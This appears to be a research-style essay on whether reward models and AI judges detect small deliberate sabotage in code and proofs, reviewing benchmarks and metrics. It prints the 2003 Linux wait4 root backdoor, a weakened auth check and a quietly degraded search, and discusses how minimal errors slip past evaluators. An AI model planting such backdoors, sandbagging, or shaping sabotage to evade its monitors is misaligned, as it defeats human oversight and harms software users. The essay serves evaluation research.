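# Can reward models and AI judges catch small deliberate sabotage in code and proofs?

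## What small sabotage looks like, and how detection is measured

AI systems now write much of the code and many of the proofs that people rely on, and other AI systems often check that work. A *learned evaluator* is a model that checks work by reading it and giving a score or a verdict. A test suite, by contrast, runs the code, and a proof checker works through the logic mechanically. *Minimal sabotage* is a deliberate, harmful change that its maker keeps as small as possible, leaving the rest of the work sound. It can be one altered line of code, one false step in a proof, or slightly worse work than the worker could have done. People who use learned evaluators to train other models, or to guard against those models, need to know how often the evaluators notice such changes.

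### The Linux kernel in 2003

One well-documented case is much older than today's language models. In early November 2003 an intruder got into a server that held a public copy of the source code of the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, and added two lines to a function named `wait4`:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

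This code looks like a routine error check, but it can give the calling program full control of the computer. It appears to return an error if a program calls `wait4` with a certain odd pair of options and the user running the program is user number 0. In C, however, `==` compares two values, while a single `=` assigns one. The second half of the condition uses `=`, so it sets the user number to 0, and user 0 is "root", the account that may do anything on the machine, as Freedom to Tinker's *the linux backdoor attempt of 2003* (2013) explains. The assignment has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the condition fails, the error line never runs, and the program continues as root.

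Whoever wrote this change did so carefully. Szepe (2003), a reader of the kernel developers' mailing list, pointed out that the extra parentheses around the assignment stop the compiler from printing a warning. In *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks*, a news report from the day after the discovery, Poulsen (2003) quoted the security consultant Ryan Russell, who called the change "indistinguishable from an accidental bug".

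An automatic check, not a reader, found the change. The master copy of the kernel was kept in a different system, BitKeeper. A scheduled job exported it to the public server, then compared checksums (short fingerprints computed from a file's contents) on the two sides, and one file didn't match. Larry McVoy, whose company ran BitKeeper, fixed the file and told the mailing list. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) wrote that the stray log entries lacked the usual pointer to an approved change, but that it was "not a big deal". When another developer asked out of curiosity what the changed lines were, McVoy posted them. One programmer thought they looked odd, and about twenty minutes after the post another, Chad Kitching, suggested that they were a backdoor, which McVoy said he had missed.

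People recognised the trick only after a mechanical comparison had isolated the two lines, and even the man who had just removed those lines had not seen what they did. Dilger (2003) wrote in the same thread that the change might have taken a good while to find without the comparison. McVoy said it would have gone unnoticed, and developers who used the public copy would have passed it on in their own patches.

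The comparison worked because a trusted master copy existed. A new function or proof written by an AI system has no master copy, so the checker has to judge the text itself. Fixed rules help a little. Jones (2003), in *Thwarted Linux backdoor*, noted that the coding standard for voting machines already banned assignments inside conditions, and that automatic tools could flag them. But he expected an attacker this skilled to follow the coding rules and hide the backdoor some other way.

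### Three kinds of minimal sabotage

In code, the saboteur plants a backdoor, as in the Linux case, or weakens a check. Here a single word does it:

```python
if user.is_admin and session.is_valid:   # sound
if user.is_admin or session.is_valid:    # sabotaged: any logged-in user gets through
```

Both versions run and let a logged-in administrator in, so a test of that case alone passes either way. They differ in whether they meet the *specification*, the statement of what the code should do (or, for a proof, of what the theorem should say).

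In a proof, the saboteur inserts a step that does not follow. Ulusan, Akbudak and colleagues (2026), in *FormalRewardBench*, built 250 pairs of correct and incorrect proofs for Lean, a *proof assistant*: a program that mechanically checks every step of a proof written in its language. One of their illustrations swaps two hypotheses:

```lean
lt_trans h1 h2   -- sound: from a < b and b < c, conclude a < c
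lt_trans h2 h1   -- sabotaged: the same two facts in the wrong order
```

Lean rejects the second line. But most mathematics is written in ordinary prose, where a false step can look like a harmless rephrasing. *Pseudo-Formalization for Automatic Proof Verification* (Barkallah, Bailey and colleagues, 2026) shows an example from an attempted solution to a 2024 olympiad problem. The solution includes a lemma that a set S cannot contain both d and −d, and a later step treats the lemma as if it had shown that all nonzero elements of S have the same sign. The set {1, −2} satisfies the lemma, but its elements have opposite signs. Nothing suggests that anyone planted this error, but a saboteur could write the same line.

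Quietly degraded work is harder to pin down, because it need not contain a false line anywhere:

```python
best = max(candidates, key=score)        # full effort
best = max(candidates[:5], key=score)    # quietly worse: considers only the first five
```

The second version returns a real candidate with a real score. A reviewer needs some idea of how good the answer could have been, or a reason to ask why the search stopped at five, to object to it.

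Any of these is sabotage only if it was intended, and intent does not show in the text. In *Attempted attack on Linux kernel foiled* (Lemos, 2003), McVoy describes a Trojan horse as just a bug somebody put in on purpose. Researchers can therefore make test material by planting errors themselves. The cleanest design is the *minimal pair*, two outputs that are identical except for one change that makes one of them wrong. Many benchmarks instead collect models' unintentional mistakes, which are a different population of errors.

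### What the evaluators take in and put out

A *reward model* takes a request and one output and returns a score, where higher is better. Developers usually train it on pairs of outputs labeled with the one people preferred. If a 300-line program contains one bad line, the reward model can only give a lower score, without identifying the line or explaining the problem.

A *process reward model* scores each step of a solution. Gadetsky, Kodryan and colleagues (2026), in *Unsupervised Process Reward Models*, define it as a model that reads the problem and the steps so far and gives the probability that the latest step is correct. The estimated chance that the first error is at a given step is the chance that every earlier step is right times the chance that this one is wrong. For a three-step proof with step probabilities of 0.95, 0.90 and 0.30, the chance that the first error is at step 3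 is 0.95 × 0.90 × 0.70, or about 60%, and the chance of no error is 0.95 × 0.90 × 0.30, or about 26%.

Gadetsky and colleagues note that some process reward models estimate how likely a partial solution is to end in the right final answer, rather than whether each step is correct. The difference is serious for sabotage, because these models may give a high score to a false step if a solver can still reach the right answer from it.

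An *AI judge* is a general language model instructed to read an output and give a verdict ("valid" or "invalid"), a grade, or, if it sees two outputs, a preference. It often writes out its reasoning first, including a *diagnosis*, the reason for the verdict. The diagnosis can be wrong even when the verdict is right. *AdvancedMathBench* (Kong, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested for this on 888 model-written proofs that experts had annotated. GPT-5.5 at its highest reasoning setting rejected 73.3% of the invalid proofs, but the share fell to 55.1% when counting only rejections that matched the experts on what was wrong and where. If a judge rejects a sabotaged proof because of a harmless remark, the verdict is right only by luck, and whoever investigates will look in the wrong place.

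### The measures

Two numbers describe an evaluator that gives yes-or-no verdicts. The *detection rate* is the share of bad items that it flags, and the *miss rate* is the share of bad items that it doesn't. The *false-alarm rate* is the share of sound items that it wrongly flags. Neither the detection rate nor the false-alarm rate means much alone, since an evaluator that flags everything has a perfect detection rate but also flags every sound item.

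Papers often fold the two into one figure. *Balanced accuracy* is the plain average of the evaluator's accuracy on bad items and its accuracy on sound ones. *Balanced F1* is the harmonic mean of the same two accuracies, which falls towards zero when either of them does. With detection rate d and false-alarm rate f:

balanced accuracy = (d + (1 − f)) / 2

balanced F1 = 2 · d · (1 − f) / (d + (1 − f))

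Suppose two judges each read 100 sabotaged items and 100 sound ones, then pick the sound item from each of 100 minimal pairs. The judges and their results are invented for illustration.

| Measure | Calculation | Judge A | Judge B | Coin toss |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Detection rate | flags on sabotaged items ÷ 100 | 60% | 14% | 50% |
| False-alarm rate | flags on sound items ÷ 100 | 10% | 2% | 50% |
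| Balanced accuracy | average of d and 1 − f | 75% | 56% | 50% |
| Balanced F1 | harmonic mean of d and 1 − f | 72% | 24.5% | 50% |
| Pairwise accuracy | pairs with the right pick in both orders ÷ 100 | 64% | 40% | 25% |

Judge B approves nearly everything. Its balanced accuracy of 56% makes it look merely weak, but its balanced F1 reveals the problem. GPT-4.1, an older OpenAI model, performed similarly on *Hard2Verify* (Pandit, Xu and colleagues, 2025), a benchmark of 200 model-written solutions to olympiad-level problems in which mathematicians marked every step. When judging single steps, it scored 56.2 on balanced accuracy and 24.7 on balanced F1. Together, these scores imply that it was right about 98% of the time on one type of step (correct or incorrect) and about 14% on the other. Pandit and colleagues found that weak verifiers accept nearly every step as correct, so the 14% must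 be the detection rate.

Balanced scores also don't show which kind of error a judge tends to make. A judge with a 90% detection rate and a 40% false-alarm rate gets the same balanced scores as Judge A, 75% and 72%, but misses a quarter as much sabotage and raises four times as many false alarms. Which judge is preferable depends on how much harm misses and false alarms each cause, and on how common sabotage is.

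An experimenter can also move the same evaluator between such positions. With a process reward model, the experimenter picks the score below which a step counts as wrong, and a stricter cut-off raises both the detection rate and the false-alarm rate. With an AI judge, the experimenter can ask for several readings and reject the work if any of them finds a fault. Barkallah and colleagues point out that extra readings can only add flags. If Judge A read everything eight times and its readings were independent (real ones probably aren't), its detection rate would rise from 60% to 99.9% and its false-alarm rate from 10% to 57%.

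A judge's score also depends on what counts as a catch. On the same Hard2Verify solutions, GPT-5 scored a balanced F1 of 89.5 when it only had to judge whether the whole solution was right, 85.8 when it had to label each step, and 69.7 when it had to name the first wrong step. Whole-solution scoring is the most lenient because a judge gets credit for rejecting a flawed solution even if it misidentifies the error.

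### "Positive" means opposite things in different papers

Pandit and colleagues, Kong and colleagues, and *Pessimistic Verification for Open Ended Math Questions* (2025) treat a valid proof as the positive case, so their "true positive rate" is accuracy on valid proofs and their "true negative rate" is the detection rate. Barkallah and colleagues, who work partly on the same Hard2Verify solutions, treat "contains error" as positive, so their "recall" is the detection rate. A "false positive" is therefore a missed error under the first convention and a false alarm under the second.

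Kong and colleagues report a true positive rate of 96.4% for Claude Opus 4.8, meaning that it accepted 96.4% of the valid proofs. A reader could easily mistake this for the share of bad proofs it caught. That share, its detection rate, was 37.9%, and its false-alarm rate, the share of valid proofs it rejected, was 3.6%. To avoid this ambiguity, the sections that follow use the terms detection rate and false-alarm rate, whatever the original paper called them.

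### Pairs, and why guessing scores 25%

Many benchmarks measure *pairwise accuracy*, which is how often an evaluator prefers a sound item to a bad one, instead of requiring a verdict on each item. A reward model scores the two items separately, and the one with the higher score counts as its preference. Ulusan and colleagues require the sound proof to score strictly higher, so a judge that gives both proofs eight out of ten fails on that pair. Such ties are plausible with minimal pairs.

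An AI judge that sees both items at once brings a further complication, position bias: many judges lean towards whichever item comes first, or second, regardless of content. The usual remedy, which *On the Shelf Life of Fine-Tuned LLM-Judges* (2025) describes as standard practice, is to show each pair twice with the order reversed, and to give credit only if the judge picks the right item both times. A judge that tosses a coin has a 1/2 chance of being right in one order and a 1/2 chance in the other, so it earns credit on 1/2 × 1/2 = 1/4 of the pairs. That is the 25% baseline. (*RewardBench 2* (2025) also has a guessing baseline of 25%, for an unrelated reason: the evaluator there picks one correct answer out of four.)

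A judge that can't tell which item is correct may score above or below the 25% expected from coin-tossing. One that always picks the first item scores 0%, because it is wrong in one of the two orders. Ulusan and colleagues found that DeepSeek-Prover-V2-7B, a model that writes Lean proofs, came close to this. It chose the correct proof 94.9% of the time when that proof came first, 9.8% when it came second, and 9.4% in both orders. A judge with a stable but irrelevant preference, such as for the item with more commas, would be right in both orders about half the time and score about 50%. A score between 25% and 50% is therefore better than coin-tossing, but it doesn't necessarily show that the judge can recognize the correct item.

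The agreement figures help distinguish these cases. Claude Opus 4.5 picked the correct proof in both orders for 59.8% of pairs and gave the same answer in both orders for 64.9%, so when it was consistent it was right about 92% of the time. Selene-1-70B, a model trained specifically for judging, picked the correct proof in both orders for 44.4% of pairs, well above the 25% expected from random guessing. But it was consistent on 78.4% of pairs, so it was right on only about 57% of those, not far above the 50% expected from a consistent preference unrelated to correctness.

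Even a high pairwise score is not a detection rate, because the judge has hints that it wouldn't have when reading a single new piece of work. It knows that exactly one of the two items is bad and, when they form a minimal pair, it can find the suspicious spot by comparing them. The checksum comparison gave the kernel developers roughly the same help in 2003.

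## The case that AI judges can already catch most small sabotage

The optimistic view of AI judges rests on four premises:

- Checking a piece of work is easier than producing it, so a model that can write good code or proofs should be able to judge them.
- A model doesn't tire. It can read line 900 as carefully as line 1 and then read everything again, while human reviewers skim.
- Current models already have most of the ability that checking requires. When they miss an error, better instructions would often have drawn it out.
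- That ability grows with each generation of models.

If all four are true, a better-instructed judge or next year's model would catch most of the planted errors that judges miss today.

This argument combines claims from different sources, none of which concludes that AI judges can catch a saboteur. In *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs*, McAleese, Pokorny and colleagues (2024) start from the idea that checking is easier, but they apply it to people judging AI output. They also expect model critics to keep improving while human intelligence stays the same. In *Do We Need Frontier Models to Verify Mathematical Proofs?*, Naik, Shabadi and colleagues (2026) mention the ease of checking only as a common opinion, but they argue that even fairly small models can already check proofs. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) gives the most striking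 figure on improvement. Language models found under 20% of the security flaws in CyberGym, an academic benchmark, at the start of 2025 and over 85% in 2026.

### OpenAI's critics and the planted bugs

McAleese and colleagues worked at OpenAI, and their experiment is an early test of models against bugs that people had planted on purpose. They paid contractors to take code that ChatGPT had written and edit a subtle bug into it. The contractors then described the bug as if they had caught it in a code review. One illustration in the paper is a function that should return n empty lists:

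```python
return [[] for _ in range(n)]   # sound: n separate lists
return [[]] * n                 # tampered: one list, referred to n times
```

The two results look identical when printed. But in the tampered version, adding an item to one list adds it to all of them.

OpenAI asked the contractors to check that a model critic missed each bug in at least one of three attempts. The researchers didn't enforce this rule strictly, but they found that it made the bugs noticeably subtler. These bugs are close to minimal sabotage because they were small, deliberate and adjusted to get past a particular checker.

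The main critic, CriticGPT, was a GPT-4-family model that wrote comments attached to quoted pieces of code. OpenAI trained it on contractors' rankings of critiques. The human reviewers it was compared with came from the pool OpenAI used to train ChatGPT. They reported a median of five years' Python experience, took a median of about 50 minutes per review, and could run the code.

Both CriticGPT and ordinary ChatGPT caught substantially more of the planted bugs than these reviewers, though the paper charts the shares without printing the numbers. Raters who didn't know who had written each critique preferred CriticGPT's to the human one more than 80% of the time on planted bugs, and 63% of the time on bugs ChatGPT had made on its own. McAleese and colleagues attribute the reviewers' lower catch rate mainly to their shorter reviews, then to unfamiliarity with particular libraries, and then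 to the difficulty of some bugs. The shorter reviews are the study's best evidence for the premise that AI judges read without tiring.

The experiment also supports the premises about hidden ability and growth. Larger models missed fewer bugs, and so did models trained specifically as critics. By a rough extrapolation, ordinary ChatGPT would have needed about 30 times more pretraining compute to match the specially trained critic. The researchers also trained classifiers to predict only whether someone had tampered with the code. In the tenth of cases where the largest classifier was most confidently wrong, critics still caught the planted bug about 54% of the time. A model that fails to give tampered code a bad score may still find the fault when it has to write a critique.

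The AI critiques also contained many more invented problems and petty complaints than the human ones, and the critics that invented more bugs tended to catch more real ones. Contractors who edited CriticGPT's comments caught about as many bugs as CriticGPT alone and invented fewer, so they helped mostly by deleting false comments. The study gives no false-alarm rate in the sense used here, because all the code in its main tests contained a known bug. At the setting used for most results, CriticGPT commented on an average of four places per answer. A reader who doesn't know whether the code has a bug has to work out which of those comments, if any, matter.

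In one experiment, McAleese and colleagues showed contractors two solutions to a hard competition problem, only one of which passed its tests, and gave them 20 minutes to pick the right one without running anything. Critiques from an early GPT-4-sized critic didn't significantly help. The researchers suspect this was because they had sampled many solutions to find failures that were hard to spot but gave the critic only one try. A saboteur with more computing power than the judge would have the same advantage.

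These models are several generations old, and the code was short, usually a few dozen lines in one file. The study is mainly useful as history. It shows that by mid-2024, models were already better than paid reviewers at finding small planted bugs, though they also made many false complaints.

### Drawing out an ability that is already there

Naik and colleagues asked how much of a judge's failure comes from lack of ability. They tested two frontier models at the time, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, and four smaller open ones, GPT-OSS-20B, GPT-OSS-120B, Qwen3.5-35B and Qwen3.5-122B. OpenAI and Google have since released stronger models. The models judged model-written proofs for olympiad-level problems from three collections (IMO-GradingBench, ProofArena and ProofBench), which human experts had graded. In the two collections graded from 0 to 7, only a 7 counted as correct.

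Balanced accuracy, averaged over the three collections and three differently worded prompts, ranged from 76.6% for Qwen3.5-35B to 87.7% for Gemini 3.1 Pro at its low reasoning setting. That is a small gap for such a large difference in size. Most of it came from misses, since the small models' miss rate was on average 13.3 points higher than the frontier models' and their false-alarm rate only 1.1 points higher. When Naik and colleagues asked the same question three times, small models were also less consistent, giving three matching verdicts up to about 25% less often than frontier models.

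The prompt's wording mattered more than the model's size. One prompt that demanded strict step-by-step checking cut the balanced accuracy of GPT-5.2 at high reasoning by 27.3%. It brought most models' miss rates close to zero, but largely by making them reject correct proofs.

To see why judges miss errors, Naik and colleagues read the verdicts in which a model had accepted a flawed proof. They describe two patterns, which they found in all the models:

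- *Repeating the flaw.* The judge restates the bad step in its own analysis and approves it. In one example, GPT-OSS-120B accepted an invalid combination of inequalities without looking into it.
- *Repairing the proof silently.* The judge notices that something is missing, makes up the argument that would fill the gap, and then grades the proof as if the argument had been there. In the example, the proof had left out part of a case analysis.

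A judge that silently repairs a proof by supplying a missing argument evidently knows enough mathematics to notice the gap, which supports the optimistic view in one respect. One prompt in the study uses this ability by instructing the judge to try to repair the proof and to reject it if the repair requires any concrete change.

The researchers then had Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, search for prompts that would lead GPT-OSS-120B to the real error in each of 140 flawed proofs. This produced twelve prompts. One, for example, tells the judge to look for conclusions that don't follow, and another tells it to try to refute every stated lemma with a small counterexample. Between them, the twelve prompts led the judge to all but 3 of the 140 errors, though the paper's own list of contributions gives the number missed as 5. With the strictest single prompt, which tells the judge to assume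 that the proof is wrong until convinced otherwise, it found only 108, or 77%. An error counted as found only if the judge rejected the proof and identified the right error, although other models did most of the marking. GPT-5 Mini wrote the descriptions of the errors with the help of reference solutions, and the researchers checked 15 of them by hand.

The best result for AI judges is 137 of 140 errors flagged, but that rate shouldn't be expected on new work, because the search kept revising the prompts until they caught the errors in these same proofs. Naik and colleagues asked for general prompts, yet the one about lemmas includes a specific warning about removing an edge from a tree and the sizes of the pieces, which seems to come from one particular faulty proof. With the same twelve prompts, GPT-OSS-20B also flagged 137 errors, but Qwen3.5-35B flagged only 90, and about 15% of each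 model's flags didn't match the recorded error.

The other problem is false alarms. Some of the twelve prompts rejected up to 37.3% of correct proofs when used alone. Rejecting a proof whenever any of the twelve prompts flags it would raise at least as many false alarms as the worst single prompt, because extra readings can only add flags.

So the researchers ran a second search for a good balance between the two kinds of error. The resulting system calls the model twelve times, five with the same general grading prompt and seven with specialised ones, and accepts a proof if at least eight calls find it correct. On IMO-GradingBench, GPT-OSS-120B with this vote had a detection rate of 86% and a false-alarm rate of 14%. Without any vote, GPT-5.2 at high reasoning had a detection rate of 95% and a false-alarm rate of at least 14%.

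Asking the best single prompt twelve times did less well than the vote, because the repeated answers were highly correlated. Putting all the instructions into one long prompt was hardly better than the ordinary prompt. The gains also carried over to ProofBench, where Qwen3.5-35B's balanced accuracy rose from 75.5% to 85.2%. The search had used neither that model nor those proofs, so this result is better evidence for a hidden ability than the 137.

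The voting rule can miss sabotage, though. Rejecting a proof takes five objections, so a proof whose error is detected by only one specialised prompt passes with eleven votes in favour. The rule lowers false alarms by ignoring lone objections, but a carefully hidden error is the kind most likely to draw only one. A developer could send every lone objection to a person instead, but that person would have to check all the false alarms that the vote removed.

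The detection rates also cover all flawed proofs together, so a proof graded 0 counts the same as one that lost a single point. The paper gives no separate rate for proofs with one small fault. The rates are also for olympiad problems, not graduate-level mathematics.

### Tens of thousands of flaws in real software

In 2026 the evidence moved from benchmarks to software that people use. The usual measure is the number of CVEs, entries in a public catalogue of known security flaws. The security firm VulnCheck had counted 100,222 new CVEs by 13 November (KIberblick, *100.000 CVEs*, 2026). Another tracker lists 48,150 for all of 2025. Josh Bressers of VulnCheck attributes most of what the firm is seeing to AI-assisted search. Microsoft fixed 1,413 flaws in its October update alone (Kovacs, *Microsoft Patches Record 1,413 Vulnerabilities, Including Exploited Windows Zero-Day*, 2026). Its previous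 record for an entire year was 1,261, in 2020, and it credits language models for the high number of discoveries (Krebs, *Microsoft Patches More Than 1,400 Security Flaws*, 2026).

The most detailed public record is a dashboard that Anthropic (2026) keeps of flaws its Claude models have found in open-source software. The models include an early version of Claude Mythos Preview. The counts for 2 November 2026 were:

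| Stage | Findings |
|---|---|
| Candidates produced by the models | 37,966 |
| Reviewed by outside security firms | 6,376 |
| Confirmed as real by those firms | 6,009 |
| Reported to the software's maintainers | 5,087 |
| Patched, to Anthropic's knowledge | 629 |

(Of the 5,087 reports, 3,225 went to maintainers directly, without the outside firms' check.)

Some of the published flaws are as small as the sabotage described earlier. NSS, a widely used security library, set a limit of 22 where 23 items could occur. MapServer, a program that serves maps, used the wrong counter variable in a safety check. A decryption function in wolfSSL, another security library, never verified the tag that shows whether a message has been altered. Nobody suggests that these flaws were deliberate, but any of them could have served a saboteur's purpose. The projects' human reviewers had missed them, and the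 models found them without a trusted copy to compare against.

The firms confirmed 94.2% of the findings they reviewed. Anthropic calls this the "true positive rate", but it is *precision*, the share of an evaluator's flags that turn out to be right, and it doesn't measure how many flaws the models missed. Papers on proof judging use "true positive rate" for two other measures.

Critics dispute even the precision. In VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), Patrick Garrity points to curl, a common tool for transferring data. Its maintainers had rejected 19 of 34 published reports as not being vulnerabilities, confirmed six as low-severity and left nine undecided. The gap may arise partly because Anthropic counts a bug as a true positive if a security firm decides it is real, even if the maintainer doesn't intend to fix it. Some findings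 may also have skipped the firm's review, since by October Anthropic was letting maintainers sort unreviewed findings themselves. Anthropic wrote that it did this because human checking had become the bottleneck.

VulnCheck also found only 217 entries marked as fixed in the dashboard's detailed ledger, compared with 629 in the headline count, and credits Anthropic with about 0.5% of the year's CVEs. KIberblick's *Glasswing* (2026) replies that part of this criticism misreads Anthropic's figures, and that the ledger omits flaws that partners such as Microsoft and Cisco find and fix in their own products. Slow repairs matter little for the question of detection, because a flaw that a model has found still counts as a catch even if nobody has fixed it.

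### Many flaws found, unknown numbers left

The main objection to this evidence is that finding many flaws doesn't show that few remain. Calculating a detection rate requires the total number of flaws in the code, which nobody knows. Anthropic's models have 6,009 confirmed findings, and the dashboard would look the same whether they had missed 1,000 flaws in the same code (a detection rate of 86%) or 54,000 (a rate of 10%).

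The counts also show no sign of levelling off, which they should do when a search has found nearly everything it can. Candidates rose from 26,153 in early September to 37,966 in early November. *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard* (Coopersmith, 2026) listed 1,596 reported flaws in 281 projects in May, or 5.7 per project. By November the rate was 7.5. Better models, longer searches and faster reporting could all have contributed, so the rise doesn't show how many flaws are left, but it gives no reason to think the number is small.

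Overlap between separate searches would be more informative. If outside researchers find 100 flaws in some code, and a model working independently finds 90 of the same ones, the model's detection rate is probably near 90%. In the ledger, 1,654 of the 7,349 entries are marked as duplicates, but that is the share of Claude's findings that had turned up elsewhere, which helps estimate how much other searchers catch. To estimate Claude's rate, we would need the share of other people's findings that Claude had also made. Even that estimate would be too high if the other searchers used similar models that miss the same flaws.

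A defender of AI judges can answer the objection in two ways. One is to rely on tests where the total number of flaws is known, such as CyberGym, where the result was 85%, or the graded proofs, where GPT-5.2 caught 95%. The other is to point out that a judge guarding against sabotage has a narrower job than one looking for every flaw in a million lines of old code. It only has to notice what is wrong with the change it is reviewing.

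The second answer is reasonable, but the models that look for flaws have evidence from crashes that such a judge may lack. The glossary in Anthropic's *About this dashboard* (2026) defines a candidate as any distinct crash or vulnerability hypothesis, which implies that some findings came from running the program and seeing it crash. Most of the published CVEs are memory errors, which often cause crashes. A judge that reads a pull request (a proposed change to a codebase) without running it gets no such signal, and neither an `or` in place of an `and` nor a search that stops after five candidates would cause a crash. The list does include flaws that don't usually cause crashes, such as login bypasses in the chat program Rocket.Chat and wolfSSL's acceptance of forged certificates. The models can therefore find logic errors as well as memory errors, but the dashboard can't show how often they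 miss logic errors.

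## The case that small changes are where learned evaluators are weakest

One reason for pessimism is that developers train reward models on better and worse outputs that usually differ in many visible ways at once. A reward model can learn to tell these outputs apart without learning to respond to a single word or symbol that makes the work wrong, which may be all that minimal sabotage changes.

### What the training loss rewards

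For a request x with a preferred output y⁺ and a rejected output y⁻, training adjusts the reward model R to lower a quantity called the loss. Liu, Yao and colleagues (2024), in *RM-Bench*, give the standard loss for one pair as:

loss = −log σ(m), where m = R(x, y⁺) − R(x, y⁻) and σ(m) = 1 / (1 + e^(−m))

The *margin* m is the preferred output's score minus the other output's score, and σ(m) converts it into the probability that the preferred output is better. The probability is 50% and the loss is 0.69 at a margin of 0, while the probability is 99.6% and the loss is 0.004 at a margin of 5.5.

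The loss depends only on the margin m, the difference between the two outputs' scores, so the model can widen it using any feature that differs between them, whether length, layout, confident phrasing or correctness. The gradient with respect to m has size σ(−m), which falls from 0.5 at m = 0 to 0.004 at m = 5.5. Once easy cues separate the pairs by a wide margin, training does little to teach the model harder cues.

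Suppose a reward model scores proofs by eleven cues, each present or absent. Ten are on the surface, such as tidy layout, named lemmas and a confident last line. The eleventh is that every step follows. In each training pair, the preferred proof has all eleven and the rejected proof has none. Because every cue separates the pairs equally well, training raises all the weights equally from zero, say to 0.5 points each.

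| Proof | Cues present | Score |
|---|---|---|
| Fluent and sound | 11 | 5.5 |
| The same proof with one false step | 10 | 5.0 |
| Sound but plain, lacking three surface cues | 8 | 4.0 |
| Rejected proof from training | 0 | 0 |

The false step lowers the fluent proof's score by only 9%. This reward model would still prefer the sound version when comparing the two. But when it judges a single new proof, any cut-off that rejects the sabotaged proof also rejects the plain, sound one. The example also favors the reward model by making validity as easy to learn as layout. If the model learns layout first, most of the training signal is gone before it learns to check a step.

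This is an argument, not a finding, and the loss does not force the outcome. If the two sides of each training pair differed only by one planted false step, only that step could produce a margin. The argument therefore predicts that reward models trained on ordinary pairs react too much to style and too little to small errors, and that more closely matched pairs reduce the problem.

### Style against substance

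Liu, Yao and colleagues give an example much like the toy one. The reward model URM-LLaMa-3-8B gave a score of 4.48 to a correct sentence about how Schrödinger's cat illustrates quantum superposition. It gave 4.47 to the same sentence with "superposition" changed to "entanglement", which makes it false. A longer version of the false sentence got 4.66.

To measure how often this happens, their benchmark, RM-Bench, includes each correct and each wrong answer in three styles: short, detailed, and detailed with formatting. In "easy" comparisons the correct answer has the more elaborate style, in "normal" ones the styles match, and in "hard" ones the wrong answer has the more elaborate style. A reward model that ignored style would do equally well on all three. In *DynaCF*, Liu, Miao and colleagues (2026) trained a reward model from Qwen3-4B, a small open model, with the ordinary loss. It preferred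 the correct answer in 91.3% of easy comparisons, 74.4% of normal ones and 41.3% of hard ones, while random guessing would get 50%. When they gave less weight to training pairs on which the model's preference depended on surface features, the hard score rose to 50.0%.

These scores only partly measure how well reward models detect small changes. For the 129 chat questions in RM-Bench, GPT-4o made the wrong answers by inserting factual errors into correct ones. For code and mathematics, the correct and wrong answers are separate attempts, which may differ throughout.

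In *reWordBench*, Wu, Yasunaga and colleagues (2025) found a cruder problem in an older benchmark, RewardBench. In its mathematics part, every correct solution had its final answer in a box, and every wrong one had it under an "Answer" heading. When they swapped the two formats, reward models' accuracy fell from above 95% to as low as 73%.

The prediction about better pairs also has some support. *Skywork-Reward-V2* (2025) describes reward models trained with the same loss but on 26 million carefully filtered pairs. The version built on Qwen3-8B scored 70.1% on hard comparisons, against 49.8% for the model that Liu, Miao and colleagues trained from the same base with the ordinary loss. The best standard version, built on Llama-3.1-8B, scored 95.0% on normal comparisons and 86.5% on hard ones. Much of the weakness therefore comes from the training data, and developers can reduce it.

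*Long-form RewardBench* (Huang, He and colleagues, 2026) includes a test closer to minimal sabotage. False facts or harmful phrases were inserted into answers of 1,000 to 8,000 tokens (word pieces), about one per thousand tokens, and a matching answer had a sound counterpart at each of the same places. The August 2024 version of GPT-4o did worse on longer answers and on errors in the middle. A score-only reward model from the first Skywork series was less affected by length but caught errors more often near the end. Both results are evidence against the optimistic premise that a model checks line 900 as well as line 1, though both models are old.

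### Process reward models have a different weakness

Developers usually train process reward models on single steps, each labelled right or wrong, so the argument about pairs doesn't apply directly. Agrawal, Chakraborty and colleagues (2026), in *The Hidden Bias of Process Reward Models*, point to an imbalance in the labels instead. In PRM800K, a widely used training set, 73.1% of steps are correct, although only 14.2% of solutions are correct throughout. A model that leans towards "correct" will therefore usually be right about a step. On PRMBench, a test of single steps, Qwen2.5-Math-PRM-7B accepted 95% of correct steps but also 69% of wrong ones.

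Some of the labels are also wrong. A common automatic method counts a step as right if a solver continuing from it reaches the correct final answer in any of several attempts, even if the solver had to repair a false step. In *Towards Robust Process Reward Modeling via Noise-aware Learning*, Xie, Xu and colleagues (2026) had a language model find such repairs and stopped counting them as successes. They trained the same 7B model on the original and on the corrected labels. On flawed solutions to school-level problems, correcting the labels raised its detection rate from 33.2% to 55.6%, and further cleaning during training raised it to 65.5%, with slightly fewer false alarms. On olympiad problems, the rate rose from 12.6% to only 35.8%.

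Agrawal and colleagues used the pairwise loss again, this time on pairs of steps that continue the same partial solution. The miss rate on PRMBench fell from 69% to 47%, while the false-alarm rate rose from about 4% to 13%. Extra data with the ordinary single-step loss lowered the miss rate only to 67%. This fits the prediction that the pairwise loss works better when the two outputs have nearly everything in common. However, many of the added "wrong" steps were later steps from the same solution, inserted too early, rather than false steps.

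### Edits that should and should not move a score

*Reward Under Attack* (Tiwari, Tomar and colleagues, 2026) directly tested how process reward models respond to edits. The researchers used GPT-4o to make eight kinds of edit to worked solutions to mathematics problems. Four preserve the meaning and should not change the score. The other four break the logic or the link to the question, and the researchers expected them to lower the score sharply.

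They tested one 7B model from each of two families. Qwen2.5-Math-PRM is designed to locate the first error, so they scored each solution by its lowest step score. Skywork-o1-Open-PRM estimates the chance of eventual success, so they used the score of the last step. Scores run from 0 to 1. The table gives the average change, with the standard deviation in brackets.

| Edit | Qwen2.5-Math-PRM-7B | Skywork-o1-Open-PRM-7B |
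|---|---|---|
| Rephrase | −0.01 (0.03) | −0.02 (0.05) |
| Use more words | −0.01 (0.02) | −0.03 (0.06) |
| Use fewer words | −0.01 (0.02) | −0.04 (0.07) |
| Reorder within a step | −0.03 (0.08) | −0.02 (0.05) |
| Swap in an unrelated question | −0.32 (0.35) | −0.20 (0.25) |
| Change the numbers in the question | −0.85 (0.25) | −0.45 (0.30) |
| Insert an unfounded assumption | −0.78 (0.35) | −0.15 (0.30) |
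| Remove the question | −0.07 (0.15) | −0.20 (0.25) |

Changes of style barely affected the scores, a better result than experience with ordinary reward models would suggest. Broken logic affected them inconsistently. One model scored solutions to an unrelated question only 0.32 points lower on average, and the other only 0.20 points lower, even though such solutions are worthless as answers.

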